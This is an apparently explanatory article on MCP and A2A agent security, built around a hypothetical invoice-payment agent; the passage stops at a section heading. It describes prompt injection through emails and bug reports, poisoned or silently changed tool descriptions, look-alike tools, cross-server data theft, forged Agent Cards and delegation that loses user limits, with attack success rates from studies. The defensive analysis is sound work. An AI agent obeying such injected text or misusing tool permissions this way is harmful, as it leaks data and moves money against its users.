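# Securing AI agents that use MCP and A2A: logging, policy enforcement, and inline blocking versus detect-and-respond

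## How agents call tools and other agents

An AI agent is software in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. A tool is a function that another program offers, such as searching a mailbox or sending an order to a bank. A tool call is the agent's structured request to run that function with given arguments. Without tools, a language model can only produce text, so it lists the steps and the user opens the calendar, finds the document and sends the email (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*). With tools, the agent takes those steps itself, even when they are wrong.

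Two open protocols standardise how agents call tools and other agents. An agent's application uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP) to find and call tools, and an agent uses the Agent2Agent protocol (A2A) to discover another agent and delegate a task to it. Both protocols specify the format of messages, but neither determines whether a given action is wise. A company that wants to monitor or restrict its agents has to start from those messages.

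### An accounts-payable agent

In a hypothetical example, a manufacturer's accounts-payable department uses an agent to process incoming invoices. The agent reads supplier emails with the `read_email` tool on one MCP server. A second MCP server connects it to the finance system, where `get_invoice` looks up an invoice and `release_payment` sends the money. When a supplier is new or its bank details have changed, the agent uses A2A to delegate a check on the supplier to another firm's agent.

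The finance system is the crown jewel here, the term security practitioners use for a system whose compromise or loss would severely harm the organisation. It can move money into accounts from which the company may never recover it. A leaked mailbox would be embarrassing and perhaps costly, but the company would stay in business. The mailbox also matters because anyone who knows its address can write to it, and the agent that reads the mail can also release payments.

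### One tool call from request to result

Suppose a clerk asks an agent to check invoice INV-20418 from a supplier, Marlow Castings, and to pay it if everything is in order. The MCP client, the part of the agent's application that sends requests, has already sent a `tools/list` message to each MCP server, the program that offers the tools. Each server replies with a name, a plain-language description and a schema of the arguments for every tool. The application gives the model these entries along with the clerk's request.

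The model then generates a request to call `get_invoice` with this invoice number. Nothing has happened in the finance system yet, because the model only generates text. The client turns the request into a `tools/call` message and sends it to the server, which checks the arguments, runs the lookup and returns a result. The client passes the result back to the model, which uses it to choose the next call, perhaps `read_email` to compare the bank details or `release_payment`. The loop runs until the model produces an answer for the clerk instead of another call.

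The tools page of the Model Context Protocol specification calls this arrangement "model-controlled" and recommends that a human always be able to deny a call. The specification words this as a SHOULD, which is a strong recommendation, rather than a MUST, which is a requirement. When an agent processes three hundred invoices overnight, no one is there to deny a call.

### What the message contains

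The request below sends the lookup over the network. It follows the MCP revision of 28 July 2026 and is shown without the headers for login and content negotiation.

```
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Mcp-Name: get_invoice
Mcp-Method: tools/call
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Content-Type: application/json

{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 17,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
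      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "ap-agent",
        "version": "1.4.0"
      },
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {
        "elicitation": {}
      }
    },
    "name": "get_invoice",
    "arguments": { "invoice_id": "INV-20418" }
  }
}
```

The body follows JSON-RPC 2.0, a general convention for calling functions on another machine with JSON messages. The `jsonrpc` field gives the version, which is always 2.0. The client picks the `id`, a number or string, and the server repeats it in its response so that the client can match each response to its request when several calls are under way. The `method` field names the operation. The `params` field holds the details of the call, where `name` is the tool and `arguments` holds the values, which must fit the schema that the server published for the tool.

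`_meta` holds information about the request itself. The official Model Context Protocol schema requires two entries: `protocolVersion`, the revision in use, and `clientCapabilities`, the optional features the client can handle. The capability here, `elicitation`, means the server may send back a question for the user. Clients should normally also include `clientInfo`, which gives the name and version of the client software. Clients report this information themselves and the protocol doesn't verify it, so the maintainers advise servers against relying on it for security decisions. The name `ap-agent` in a log entry is therefore weak evidence of which program sent the call. The body also has no standard field for the clerk who made the request or for the text that led the model to make this call.

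The three MCP headers repeat values from the body, so a gateway can read those values without parsing the JSON. A gateway is a proxy that a company uses to log, check or refuse agent traffic. According to the Model Context Protocol post on the release candidate, servers reject a request if its headers and body don't match.

The finance server's response might look like this:

```
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
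  "id": 17,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [
      {
        "type": "text",
        "text": "INV-20418, Marlow Castings, EUR 18,400.00, due 2026-10-30, approved"
      }
    ],
    "isError": false
  }
}
```

A `resultType` of `complete` means that the server has finished. `content` is a list of blocks for the model to read, usually text, but it can also include images, audio and files. A server may add a machine-readable copy in `structuredContent`. The `isError` field marks failures inside the tool. If the invoice number had the wrong format, the server would return an ordinary result with `isError` set to true. The client should pass that result to the model, which can correct the argument and try again. A request for a tool that doesn't exist produces a JSON-RPC error with a numeric code instead.

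The server can also return an unfinished result, with `resultType` set to `input_required`. For `release_payment`, the finance server could return a request for the clerk to confirm the amount and the account. The client collects the answer and resends the original call with a new `id` and the answer in the `inputResponses` field. Supabase, a company that hosts databases, wants to use this mechanism for similar confirmations, and its head of product gave the cost of a new project and a query that would delete data as examples. The confirmation works only if the server's developer has built it and the client has declared `elicitation`.

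### Local and remote servers

Messages have the same meaning however they travel, and Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) of the transports defines two standard ways to carry them. In the first, called stdio, the client launches the server as a process on its own machine. The two exchange messages, one per line, over standard input and standard output, the text channels that an operating system gives every program. Stdio doesn't use the HTTP headers described above, and no MCP message crosses the network.

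The second transport is Streamable HTTP. The server runs remotely, in the company's data centre or at a software vendor, and the client sends each message as a web request to a single address. The accounts-payable agent uses both transports, because its mail server is a local process and its finance server is remote. A security product on the network could therefore read every call to `release_payment` if it could decrypt the traffic, but it would see no MCP messages for `read_email`.

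### What the July 2026 revision changed

Under the previous revision, of November 2025, a client had to send an `initialize` message before it could make the request shown above. The server replied with a session identifier, which the client attached to every later message. That identifier tied the client to the copy of the server that issued it. The new revision removes both this handshake and the session identifier, according to the Model Context Protocol (2026) release post. Each request now carries its own protocol version and capabilities, and any copy of the server can answer it. A client can call `server/discover` to learn a server's features in advance, but it doesn't have to.

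Some tasks still need to keep state between calls. A finance server that builds up a batch of payments can return an identifier for the batch, which the model passes back as an ordinary argument in later calls. This moves the state from the transport, where it was hidden from the model, into the conversation. Self-describing requests help gateways, but analysts lose the session ID that used to group an agent's calls in the logs.

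Old and new versions will likely run side by side for some time. The change breaks compatibility, but clients and servers can support several revisions at once, and every request declares which one it uses. If a server doesn't support the declared version, it returns an error listing the versions it does support, according to the official Model Context Protocol page on versioning. The main development kits supported the new revision on the day of release, while Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) described support in the company's own products as still rolling out. A company with dozens of MCP servers from different vendors will probably see both formats in its traffic.

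### Delegating a task over A2A

Checking a new supplier can take hours and may involve company registers, bank records and a person's judgement, so it is hard to express as a single function with fixed arguments. A2A instead treats the other side as an agent with a job to do. In its guide to A2A version 1.0, the Agentic AI Foundation, an industry body that hosts MCP, reduces the protocol to four objects: the Agent Card, the message, the task and the artifact.

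The Agent Card is a JSON document that lists an A2A agent's identity, skills, address and accepted credentials. The firm that runs the supplier-check agent publishes the card at a fixed path on its web server, `/.well-known/agent-card.json`. The accounts-payable agent fetches the card and reads the `supportedInterfaces` field to find out where to send messages and in which format. This field is an ordered list with one entry for each format the supplier-check agent accepts.

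The accounts-payable agent then calls `SendMessage`. According to the official A2A site, a message is one turn of communication between the client and the remote agent. It has a role, which marks the side that sent it, and one or more parts. A part contains text, raw bytes, a web address or structured data. Here a text part describes the check, and a data part holds the supplier's name, registration number and bank account.

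When the supplier-check agent receives the request, it opens a task, the unit of work in A2A. A task has an ID, a context ID, a state, a history and eventually artifacts, which are its outputs. Here the artifact is a short report with a verdict on the bank account. The state starts at `TASK_STATE_SUBMITTED` and normally passes through a working state to a completed one, though the supplier-check agent can also reject the task or suspend it until the accounts-payable agent supplies further credentials. While the task is open, the accounts-payable agent can poll it with `GetTask`, follow its progress with `SubscribeToTask` or cancel it with `CancelTask`. Because the task lasts longer than any single request, its ID links the whole exchange, which MCP no longer offers a way to do.

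The two agents don't need to share their plans, reasoning or tools, a principle that the A2A specification calls opaque execution. This lets competing vendors' agents work together without exposing how they are built. The manufacturer can log the message it sent and the artifact it received, but it can't see which registers the other firm's agent consulted, or whether that agent passed the job on to a third agent, unless the other firm discloses this.

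### History, governance and adoption

Anthropic released MCP in November 2024 and donated it in December 2025 to the Agentic AI Foundation, a fund under the non-profit Linux Foundation. Changes to MCP go through written proposals and public working groups. The July 2026 release added two rules to this process. A proposal on the standards track cannot become final until the official test suite includes a matching test, and a feature marked for removal normally stays for at least twelve months.

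Google announced A2A in April 2025 and handed it to the Linux Foundation that June. Version 0.3 followed in July 2025. Version 1.0 arrived in early 2026 and renamed much of what a monitoring product would look for. A comparison by the Agentic AI Foundation shows, for example, that the method `message/send` became `SendMessage`.

MCP is widely used by any count, although the counts come from parties with an interest in it. Anthropic put monthly downloads of the development kits at over 400 million in July 2026, a fourfold rise within the year, and the release post of the same day gave a figure of close to half a billion for the main kits. Automated build systems download the same package repeatedly, so these figures are a better guide to how much software depends on MCP than to how many agents are running. Honeycomb, which sells monitoring software, offers a more direct measure of agent activity,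 saying in the release post that agents now make nearly 20 per cent of all its interactive queries in a month. Anthropic's directory for Claude lists more than 950 MCP servers.

There is less evidence on A2A. The project maintains development kits in six languages, but not everyone has moved to version 1.0. Documentation from the software vendor Emergence AI describes reference agents that still serve the previous version, 0.3.0.

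### Prompt injection

The loop described above is vulnerable to prompt injection, a weakness that MCP and A2A neither create nor remove. When the agent calls `read_email`, the client places the text of the email in the same context as the clerk's request, and the model cannot reliably distinguish its user's instructions from instructions in a document. In a prompt injection attack, an attacker hides instructions in content the agent reads, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. An attacker can attempt this without a password or access to the company's network, either by emailing the accounts-payable address or through an artifact from an outside agent that has itself been manipulated.

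A successful injection leaves the messages looking normal. The call to `release_payment` comes from the usual client with valid credentials, and its arguments fit the schema. Only the account number is wrong, or the payment has no business reason. The MCP maintainers recommend that clients validate tool results before the model sees them and ask the user to confirm sensitive operations. Both steps help, but validation has to recognise hostile text that an attacker can phrase in endless ways, and people who confirm hundreds of payments a day stop reading the details. A company therefore also needs to control the calls themselves.

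Inline blocking checks a call before it runs and refuses it if the check fails. Detect-and-respond lets the call run, analyses its record afterwards, alerts staff, and contains and repairs any damage. An alert a few minutes later may be enough for a stray `get_invoice` call, which only reads data. Repairing a stray `release_payment` call depends on whether the bank can still recall the money.

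## Security gaps in MCP

MCP leaves most security decisions to the developers of clients and servers. The US National Security Agency listed the resulting gaps in a May 2026 information sheet, *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, which quotes the maintainers' documentation as stating that MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level". MCP was revised on 28 July 2026, so a few of the sheet's criticisms no longer apply to the current version, but most still do.

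### Callers without a proven identity

Authorization is optional in MCP. A server may require a token with every request, or it may run any well-formed call that reaches it. The NSA found that many implementations have no authentication, and that those with a login often don't distinguish callers who may read data from callers who may change it. If the manufacturer had built its finance server without authentication, any program on the company network could call `release_payment`. The log might still show a call from `ap-agent`, because callers choose that name themselves.

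A token proves only that the caller holds a valid credential. If every agent in the department uses the same service account, the finance server can't identify which clerk requested a payment or which agent is acting for her. MCP doesn't require a credential that names both the person and the agent, and it doesn't require servers to check one.

MCP Inspector, Anthropic's tool for testing MCP servers, includes a proxy that can launch an MCP server as a local process on the developer's machine. According to GitLab's advisory database, the proxy accepted launch requests without authentication. A web page could send such a request, so a developer could lose control of the workstation just by visiting a malicious site, according to the security company Tenable. Lumelsky (2025), in *Critical RCE Vulnerability in Anthropic MCP Inspector*, described the same flaw for another security company, Oligo.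 The flaw, CVE-2025-49596, has a severity score of 9.4 out of 10, and version 0.14.1 fixed it. Both companies present the discovery as their own, but GitLab's entry credits Rémy Marot of Tenable. The NSA sheet attributes the flaw to "unverified inputs", but the US vulnerability database run by NIST classifies it more precisely as missing authentication.

A similar mistake turned up a year later in a WhatsApp MCP server. OSV's *CVE-2026-46555* (2026) records that, before version 0.2.1, part of the server accepted local requests without authentication. Any program running under the same user account could send WhatsApp messages and read that user's files. INCIBE, Spain's cybersecurity institute, notes that these programs include other MCP servers on the machine. The accounts-payable agent's mail server also runs locally, so a similar flaw would expose it to every other server the clerk has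 installed.

### Unchecked input and overloaded servers

Some of the gaps on the NSA's list are familiar from older software. Many servers don't strictly validate the structured data that MCP carries, and the NSA describes open-source agents that passed tool arguments straight to programs able to run arbitrary commands. Developers can set up a server for harmless data, such as weather reports, and later connect it to sensitive records without adding restrictions. Some servers slow down or fail under floods of requests or tasks that call themselves repeatedly. Many servers keep poor audit logs or none, which makes every other gap harder to investigate.

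The July revision helps only a little here. *Key Changes*, the Model Context Protocol's official list of differences from the previous revision, includes more expressive schemas for tool arguments and limits on schemas that would take too many resources to evaluate. The finance server can use a stricter schema to reject a malformed account number, but not to detect that a well-formed one belongs to a thief.

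### Tool descriptions that give orders

In tool poisoning, an attacker hides an instruction in a tool's name, description or schema. The model may follow that instruction during an unrelated task, even if it never calls the poisoned tool. For example, the instruction could lead the accounts-payable agent to call `release_payment` with a different account number. Users normally don't see the hidden text, according to *Beyond the Protocol* (2025), a study of attacks by malicious MCP servers. MCP doesn't require anyone to inspect a description before it reaches the model.

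In *MCPTox*, Wang, Gao and colleagues (2025) measured how often such attacks succeed. They added a poisoned entry to the tool lists of 45 live MCP servers, which had 353 tools in total, then gave each model an ordinary request and recorded which tools it tried to call. An attack counted as successful only if the model used a legitimate tool to carry out the hidden instruction. Success rates averaged 36.5 per cent across 20 model settings, ranging from 5.1 per cent for Qwen3-14b with its reasoning mode off to 72.8 per cent for o1-mini. Even Claude 3.7 Sonnet, which refused most often, did so in less than 3 per cent of cases. When an attack failed, the model had usually ignored the instruction without refusing it.

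The most effective attacks in this study left the user's intended call in place and changed one of its arguments. They succeeded 46.7 per cent of the time, while attacks that made the model call a different tool averaged 36.7 or 26.7 per cent, depending on how they were triggered. Changed arguments are also more dangerous for a payment system, because a rule that checks only which tool an agent calls would let the altered payment through. Better reasoning didn't protect the models. Attacks on Qwen3-8b succeeded in 14.0 per cent of cases with reasoning off and 41.8 per cent with it on.

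Choosing a strong, newer model reduces the risk from some poisoned tool descriptions but not from all of them. *COPEX* (Birhan, Rostamzadeh and colleagues, 2026) ran nine models through the same agent loop, with 16 MCP servers offering 75 tools, and tested each model 15 times against each type of attack. Descriptions designed to change the user's arguments never worked on Claude Opus 4.7, but they worked in 10 of 15 runs on GPT-5.5 and in all 15 on Gemini 3.1. Descriptions that demanded an unnecessary extra call did work on Opus 4.7, in 6 of 15 runs.

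In two smaller comparisons, *MCP Pitfall Lab* (2026) tested older OpenAI models and *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (2026) tested tools that web pages offer to agents in a browser. The table gives average success rates for hostile descriptions in all four studies.

| Study | Models | Conditions | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wang and colleagues, August 2025 | 20 settings, including o1-mini, GPT-4o-mini and Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 45 live servers, 1,348 test cases | 36.5% |
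| *MCP Pitfall Lab*, April 2026 | GPT-4.1-mini, GPT-4.1-nano, GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini | 860 completed runs | 22.6% |
| *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning*, June 2026 | GPT-5.4, Claude Opus 4.6, Gemini 2.5 Flash | Four task scenarios, five attacks based on a tool's description | 0% to 59%, depending on the attack |
| Birhan and colleagues, October 2026: changed arguments | Nine models, including Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 | 16 servers, 135 runs | 43.0% |
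| Birhan and colleagues, October 2026: unnecessary extra call | The same nine models | 16 servers, 135 runs | 51.9% |

These rates can't be ranked against each other because the studies used different attacks and definitions of success. Birhan and colleagues, for example, report a rate of 26.7 per cent for "tool poisoning", but they use the term for fabricated validation results, not hostile descriptions. All the rates also apply only once the poisoned entry has reached the model, so they don't measure how often attackers manage to get one into a company's tool list.

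### Tools that change after approval

An administrator usually reviews an MCP server once, when the company connects it. The server can later send a different description or run different code under the same tool name, which is known as a rug pull. *Beyond the Protocol* points out that MCP requires servers to register their tools but doesn't forbid later changes. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for protecting tool definitions, attributes the problem to clients, which typically don't recheck the full definition before each call and don't request new approval if the tool's name and version look the same. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of MCP threats, found that current clients don't alert users to changed definitions.

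This kind of change happened in postmark-mcp, a package on npm, a public library of JavaScript code. The package let agents send email through the delivery service Postmark. Koi Security reported in September 2025 that fifteen versions had worked as advertised before version 1.0.16 began sending a hidden copy of every email to the package's developer. Postmark said it had nothing to do with the package. Comparing old and new tool descriptions would not have revealed the change, because it was in the code. A company can guard against such an update by staying on one version until it has reviewed the next, but it can't do this for a remote server whose code it never sees.

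Models offer little protection against rug pulls, in which a trusted tool becomes malicious. In tests by Birhan and colleagues, these attacks succeeded in 56.3 per cent of runs on average. The rate was 53.3 per cent for GPT-5.5 and 86.7 per cent for Grok 4.3.

The July revision makes it easier to notice when an honest server changes its tools. According to Model Context Protocol, a client can subscribe to notices that a server's tool list has changed, and every list now includes a limit on how long the client may treat it as fresh. Servers should also return their tools in a consistent order, which makes it easier to compare two copies of a list. But the server itself sends the notices, so a hostile server can withhold them. The revision doesn't add signatures for tool definitions or require new approval when a tool changes. A client or gateway would have to keep a fingerprint of the approved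 definition and refuse calls when the current one no longer matches.

### Tools with the same name

Two MCP servers can both offer a tool called `get_invoice`. The body of a tool call gives the tool's name but not the server's, so the client has to know which server to send it to. The NSA describes systems that search public registries or local software for a matching name and load whatever they find. An attacker who publishes a tool under the name being searched for can get such a system to run their code. The NSA cites *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025) for this problem and says clients often can't specify a unique identifier for a tool or enforce a strict rule for choosing between two matches.

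A malicious tool's name doesn't have to match a legitimate tool's name exactly. *Security Threat Modeling for Emerging AI-Agent Protocols* (2026) explains that the model picks tools by their names and descriptions, so it may prefer a malicious tool that seems more relevant to the task.

In tests by Birhan and colleagues, a look-alike server succeeded in 94.8 per cent of runs and a look-alike tool in 58.5 per cent. A malicious server that registered tools to override legitimate ones succeeded in only one of 135 runs. The model receives only the text the client gives it, and a name in that text is poor evidence of who operates a server. The client can check this better because it has the server's address.

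Under the July revision, servers should identify themselves in every result. This helps with debugging, but an impostor can use the real server's name. Preventing name collisions would take an identifier that ties each tool to a verified server, and MCP doesn't require one.

### Trusted and hostile servers in one client

Many agents use several MCP servers at once. The client puts the servers' tool descriptions into the same context, so one server can attack another without communicating with it.

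Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrated this with an agent connected to a trusted WhatsApp server and an untrusted one. The untrusted server's tool descriptions manipulated the agent into exposing the user's WhatsApp messages. WhatsApp's encryption didn't protect them because the agent already had permission to read them. According to the NSA, the untrusted server showed a harmless description at installation and switched to the hostile one after its second use. A review at installation would therefore have found nothing wrong with either server.

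Reviewing servers one at a time also misses dangerous combinations of tools. *Parasites in the Toolchain* examined 1,360 MCP servers for tools that bring in outside content, read private data or send data over the network. An attacker can chain the three kinds to plant an instruction, collect private data and send it out. The study found at least one such tool on 27.2 per cent of the servers, but only two servers had all three kinds. Most such chains would therefore run across several servers. The accounts-payable agent reads outside email through one server and confidential invoices through another, so adding one tool that can send messages would complete the chain.

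Attacks across servers tend to have high measured success rates, though the evidence comes from older models. In *MCP Pitfall Lab*, attacks in which one server's descriptions influenced another server's tools succeeded in 34.5 per cent of runs, compared with 22.6 per cent for simple tool poisoning. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) reports results from MCPBench, a benchmark that compared agents that used MCP with agents that reached their tools in other ways. Attacks that spread across servers succeeded 61.3 per cent of the time with MCP and 19.7 per cent without it. The comparison is a rare attempt to separate the protocol's effect from the model's, but the gap may partly reflect how the researchers built the two kinds of agent. The tests also used Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B, all released in 2024.

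MCP has no rule that stops text from one server from influencing how an agent uses another server's tools. A company could run separate agents for trusted and untrusted servers, but it would lose some of the convenience of connecting them all to one agent. Otherwise, it needs a control outside the model that tracks data as it moves between servers.

### Tokens with too much access

An agent that connects to GitHub acts with its user's permissions, which can cover every repository the user owns. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) showed how an attacker can use those permissions to expose private data. The researchers set up an account with one public repository and several private ones, and put hidden instructions in a public issue, which anyone can post. They then asked Claude 4 Opus, running in Claude Desktop with the official GitHub MCP server, to look at the open issues. The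 agent read the private repositories and published details from them in the public one, including the fictional user's salary and plans to move abroad. Claude Desktop asks for confirmation of each tool call by default, but many users choose to always allow them.

The NSA describes this as a case where malicious or compromised tools could misuse blanket access. According to Invariant Labs, however, the tools were trustworthy and the server's code had no flaw, so GitHub couldn't fix the problem by patching the server. A token limited to the public repository would have protected the private data, although the agent would still have followed the attacker's instructions within that repository. Invariant Labs also proposed limiting an agent to one repository per session. MCP no longer has session identifiers, so a gateway that enforces this rule needs another way to decide which calls belong to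 the same session.

Stolen tokens are a separate problem because MCP authorization uses bearer tokens, which work for anyone who holds them. The NSA notes that the core specification doesn't require tokens to expire and sets no rules for replacing or revoking them. If an attacker copies a token for the finance server, it may keep working long after the company has removed the agent that used it. Copying one may not be hard, since the security firm Trail of Bits found that many MCP programs store long-term keys for outside services as plain text, often in files that every user of the machine can read.

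The July revision fixes a narrower weakness in the login process. To get a token, a client receives a temporary code from an authorization server and exchanges it. A client with many MCP servers may deal with several authorization servers, and a hostile one can try to trick it into handing over a code that an honest one issued. Under the revision, authorization servers should name themselves in their responses, and the client must check any name given against the one on record before using the code. Clients must also store their credentials separately for each issuer and never use them with another. An authorization server can still omit its name, which leaves the client with nothing to check. The official list of changes includes nothing that makes authorization mandatory, limits what a token may cover or adds rules for revocation.

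The revision also makes part of the NSA's warning about session hijacking obsolete, at least for traffic in the new format, which has no MCP session to hijack. An attacker with a stolen token can still make calls. Accidental repeats may now need more attention, because when a connection breaks before the response arrives, the client has to send the request again with a new ID. If the finance server had already released the payment, the new ID would not show that the second call was a repeat, and the server might pay the supplier twice. MCP leaves it to developers to prevent this, for example by having `release_payment` require a unique payment reference.

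### Questions from the server

The NSA also objects to MCP servers sending requests to clients. Normally the client sends requests and the server responds, but earlier revisions of the protocol also let a server request information from the user, through elicitation, or generated text from the client's model, through sampling. These requests gave a hostile server another way to reach the user and the model.

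The new revision considerably limits this route. A server can now send a question only in an unfinished reply to a client's request, so the finance server can't send the clerk an unprompted one. A gateway can also match each question to the call that prompted it. But the server still writes the question, and a hostile server can make a misleading request look routine. Sampling is due for removal but remains available, and older servers will still use the previous rules.

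### Tool output taken as instructions

An agent would still be open to prompt injection through the text it reads even if the company verified every server, froze every tool description and issued narrow tokens. For example, a mail server working as intended will deliver a supplier email that contains malicious instructions.

Sentry, whose service collects error reports from other companies' applications, faced this problem in June 2026. Tenet Security's *A Fake Bug Report Hijacks Your AI Coding Agent* (2026) describes how researchers submitted fake error reports through Sentry's public interfaces, without breaking into any system. When a developer asked a coding agent to fix the error, the agent ran the researchers' code with the developer's permissions. Tenet counted 2,388 organisations that could have been attacked this way, and saw more than 100 agents act on the reports in controlled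 tests. Some agents ran the code even after being told to ignore such instructions, according to The Next Web.

Tenet informed Sentry on 3 June, and Sentry added a content filter, as SC Media reported. A filter can stop reports that resemble known attacks, but Sentry can't reject every report that tells a developer how to fix an error, because useful reports do the same. Security software on the developer's machine can't easily spot the attack either, because an authorised agent appears to be doing its job. Tenet sells protection for AI agents, so it has an interest in making this point, but the GitHub demonstration followed the same pattern with a different service.

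Recent measurements of how often models follow hostile instructions vary widely. Birhan and colleagues placed instructions in files that the agent read during its task. Neither Claude Opus 4.7 nor Claude Sonnet 4.6 followed them in any run, while GPT-5.5 followed them every time. *INFUSE* (2026), a broader benchmark of attacks through outside content, found an average attack success rate of 19.6 per cent when a language model judged the results and 15.4 per cent when fixed rules did. The rate for Sonnet 4.6 was 3.2 per cent, but a spending limit cut many of its runs short, so the figure doesn't show that the model resisted the attacks.

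*Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation* (2026) reports the most reassuring result: only one of 43 attack scenarios succeeded against GPT-5.6 Terra. With so few scenarios, the 95 per cent confidence interval for the success rate extends to about 12 per cent. The test also used a fixed set of attacks, whereas a real attacker can keep rewording an email until it works. Even at a rate of one in 43, someone who sent a hundred hostile emails to the accounts-payable address would have about a 90 per cent chance of succeeding at least once, assuming each attempt is independent.

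## Security gaps in A2A and in delegation between agents

When the accounts-payable agent delegates a supplier check, it sends bank details to another company's agent and may release a payment based on the reply. It has to decide whether to trust that agent before they exchange any messages. It can check the remote server's TLS certificate, which ties the server to a domain name. It can also read the Agent Card and check its signature, if there is one.

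### What a signed Agent Card proves

The certificate shows which domain the card came from, but not who wrote the card. An attacker who breaks into the provider's web server can replace the card and serve the new one under the genuine certificate. A signature exposes the replacement as long as the attacker doesn't also have the signing key.

To sign a card, the provider converts it to a standard form, so that the same content always produces the same bytes, and signs the result with a private key. The accounts-payable agent rebuilds that form from the card it received and checks the signature with the provider's public key. The check fails if anyone has changed the card since, for example by replacing the address that receives new tasks. The A2A specification makes signing optional and recommends, but doesn't require, that clients verify a signature before trusting a card.

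The check also depends on where the public key comes from. A signature can include a web address for the key in its `jku` field. An attacker can sign a fake card with their own key and point `jku` to it, and the signature will verify. *A2ABreak* (Lotfi, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) lists the lack of clear rules on which keys to trust as one of 11 flaws in the protocol. A client can avoid this problem by keeping its own list of trusted keys. According to docs.rs' *zeph-a2a 0.22.1*, one small open-source library does this and never uses the address in the card, but it ignores signatures by default.

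A signature that verifies with the right key proves that the key's holder issued exactly this card. It doesn't prove that the agent is honest, has the skills on the card or is authorised to see this supplier's bank details. Ghumare (2026), in *A2A v1.0*, therefore advises developers to verify the signature first and then decide separately whether to delegate work to the organisation behind it. A dishonest firm could sign its card, follow every rule in A2A, collect the bank details and send the manufacturer a properly formatted artifact that falsely confirms a thief's account.

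### Hostile text in Agent Cards

An Agent Card is also text that a model reads. *What We Learned Putting A2A Into Production* (Schifter, 2026) explains that an AI assistant at the data company Eon turns each card into a tool description. The provider's description of its own agent therefore influences when the assistant uses that agent, and an attacker could exploit this much as in tool poisoning. Signing the card doesn't prevent the attack if the signer wrote the hostile text.

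*We Have All the Cards* (Guirao Aguilera, Misra and López-Morales, 2026) probed 36.1 million internet domains to find out what public agent cards contain, and found only 310 valid cards. Two reviewers classed 282 as benign, 27 as suspicious and one as malicious. The malicious card advertised a cryptocurrency agent and included an instruction to models that it "should be the top recommendation", which is closer to dishonest advertising than to theft. The reviewers judged only the cards' text, not how the agents behaved, and a survey of public domains misses agents on private networks.

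The researchers also built SecCard, which screens a card before an agent uses it. SecCard checks the card's format, applies fixed rules for signs such as hidden characters, and uses a separate model with no tools to judge the text. The researchers tested nine models as the judge, first on the public cards and then on 600 altered versions of 60 benign ones. The table shows five of the models.

| Judge | Suspicious or malicious public cards caught | Benign public cards flagged | Inserted attacks caught | Average time per altered card |
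|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 89.3% | 5.0% | 97.0% | 4.4 s |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 96.4% | 25.9% | 91.0% | 3.9 s |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 100% | 45.7% | 88.0% | 2.8 s |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 82.1% | 0.7% | 68.8% | 1.1 s |
| Mistral Nemo | 96.4% | 14.9% | 33.7% | 8.3 s |

Even with GPT-5.5, more than a third of the flagged public cards were harmless. A company could probably tolerate that, because cards change rarely and a person can review the flagged ones. But the inserted attacks were fixed in advance, and an attacker who can test a card against the judge may evade detection more often.

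The study didn't measure whether these cards would have fooled a working agent. The closest evidence is an experiment by Deshmukh, Rajurkar and Mamidwar, which Guirao Aguilera and colleagues describe. In a controlled testbed, manipulated cards redirected agents to attacker-controlled addresses.

### How a user's limits get lost

Suppose the manufacturer decides no agent that reads outside email should be able to move money. It gives `release_payment` to a separate treasury agent, which the accounts-payable agent can reach over A2A. The clerk may approve payments up to EUR 10,000, while the treasury agent may release up to EUR 250,000. The clerk asks the accounts-payable agent to pay invoice INV-20418 for EUR 18,400.

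| Step | Credential used | What the receiver can verify |
|---|---|---|
| The clerk instructs the accounts-payable agent | The clerk's login | Who she is and that her limit is EUR 10,000 |
| The accounts-payable agent asks the treasury agent to pay | The accounts-payable agent's service account | The request comes from the accounts-payable agent |
| The treasury agent calls `release_payment` | The treasury agent's service account | The treasury agent may release up to EUR 250,000 |

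If the accounts-payable agent doesn't enforce the clerk's limit, the payment goes through. Her identity and limit don't carry over to the second step, because A2A establishes identity separately for each connection and a task has no standard field for the person who started the chain. The accounts-payable agent could write her name and limit into the message, but the treasury agent couldn't verify them.

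The same gap lets an agent with fewer privileges use those of an agent with more, which security engineers call the confused deputy problem. The accounts-payable agent can no longer call `release_payment`, but it can ask the treasury agent to do so. An attacker who gets a prompt injection into a supplier email only has to make the accounts-payable agent send a plausible request. Moving the tool to the treasury agent adds little protection unless that agent checks who wants the payment and why.

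Eon ran into the identity problem in production. Schifter writes that one of its agents holds production credentials that the main assistant shouldn't have, so the two run separately. Another remote agent needs the user's identity, because the right answer can depend on the user's team and region. Without it, the agent would answer with a service account's rights.

Eon solved this by putting the user's identity in the context ID, which groups related tasks, and having the remote agent read the data catalogue with that user's token. This works because Eon controls both agents. If different companies ran the agents, a name in the context ID would prove very little, because the client can write any value there.

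### When a remote agent asks for more access

A2A 1.0 lets a remote agent pause a task and ask for a credential or a human's approval by setting the state to `TASK_STATE_AUTH_REQUIRED`. If the client is itself an agent working for someone else, it can pass the request up the chain. AGNTCY's *Agent Identity and Task-Based Access Control* (2026) points out that A2A deliberately leaves open what the resulting permission covers, how long it lasts and how to revoke it. Ghumare notes, however, that the state change grants no permission by itself, and that agents must not assume a credential covers later messages in the same task.

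Suppose the supplier-check agent passes part of its job to a third firm's agent, which asks for access to the manufacturer's payment history. The request travels back through the supplier-check agent and the accounts-payable agent to the clerk. She sees a request from her own company's agent, and neither she nor the service that issues the credential can identify the third firm's agent as its source.

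Lotfi and colleagues warn that a hostile agent could keep and reuse credentials that pass through it. The A2A specification recommends sending a credential directly to the agent that needs it, which would keep it away from the agents in between. But whoever sends it has to know which agent that is, and the request contains no verified record of where it began.

### Flaws in the protocol's rules

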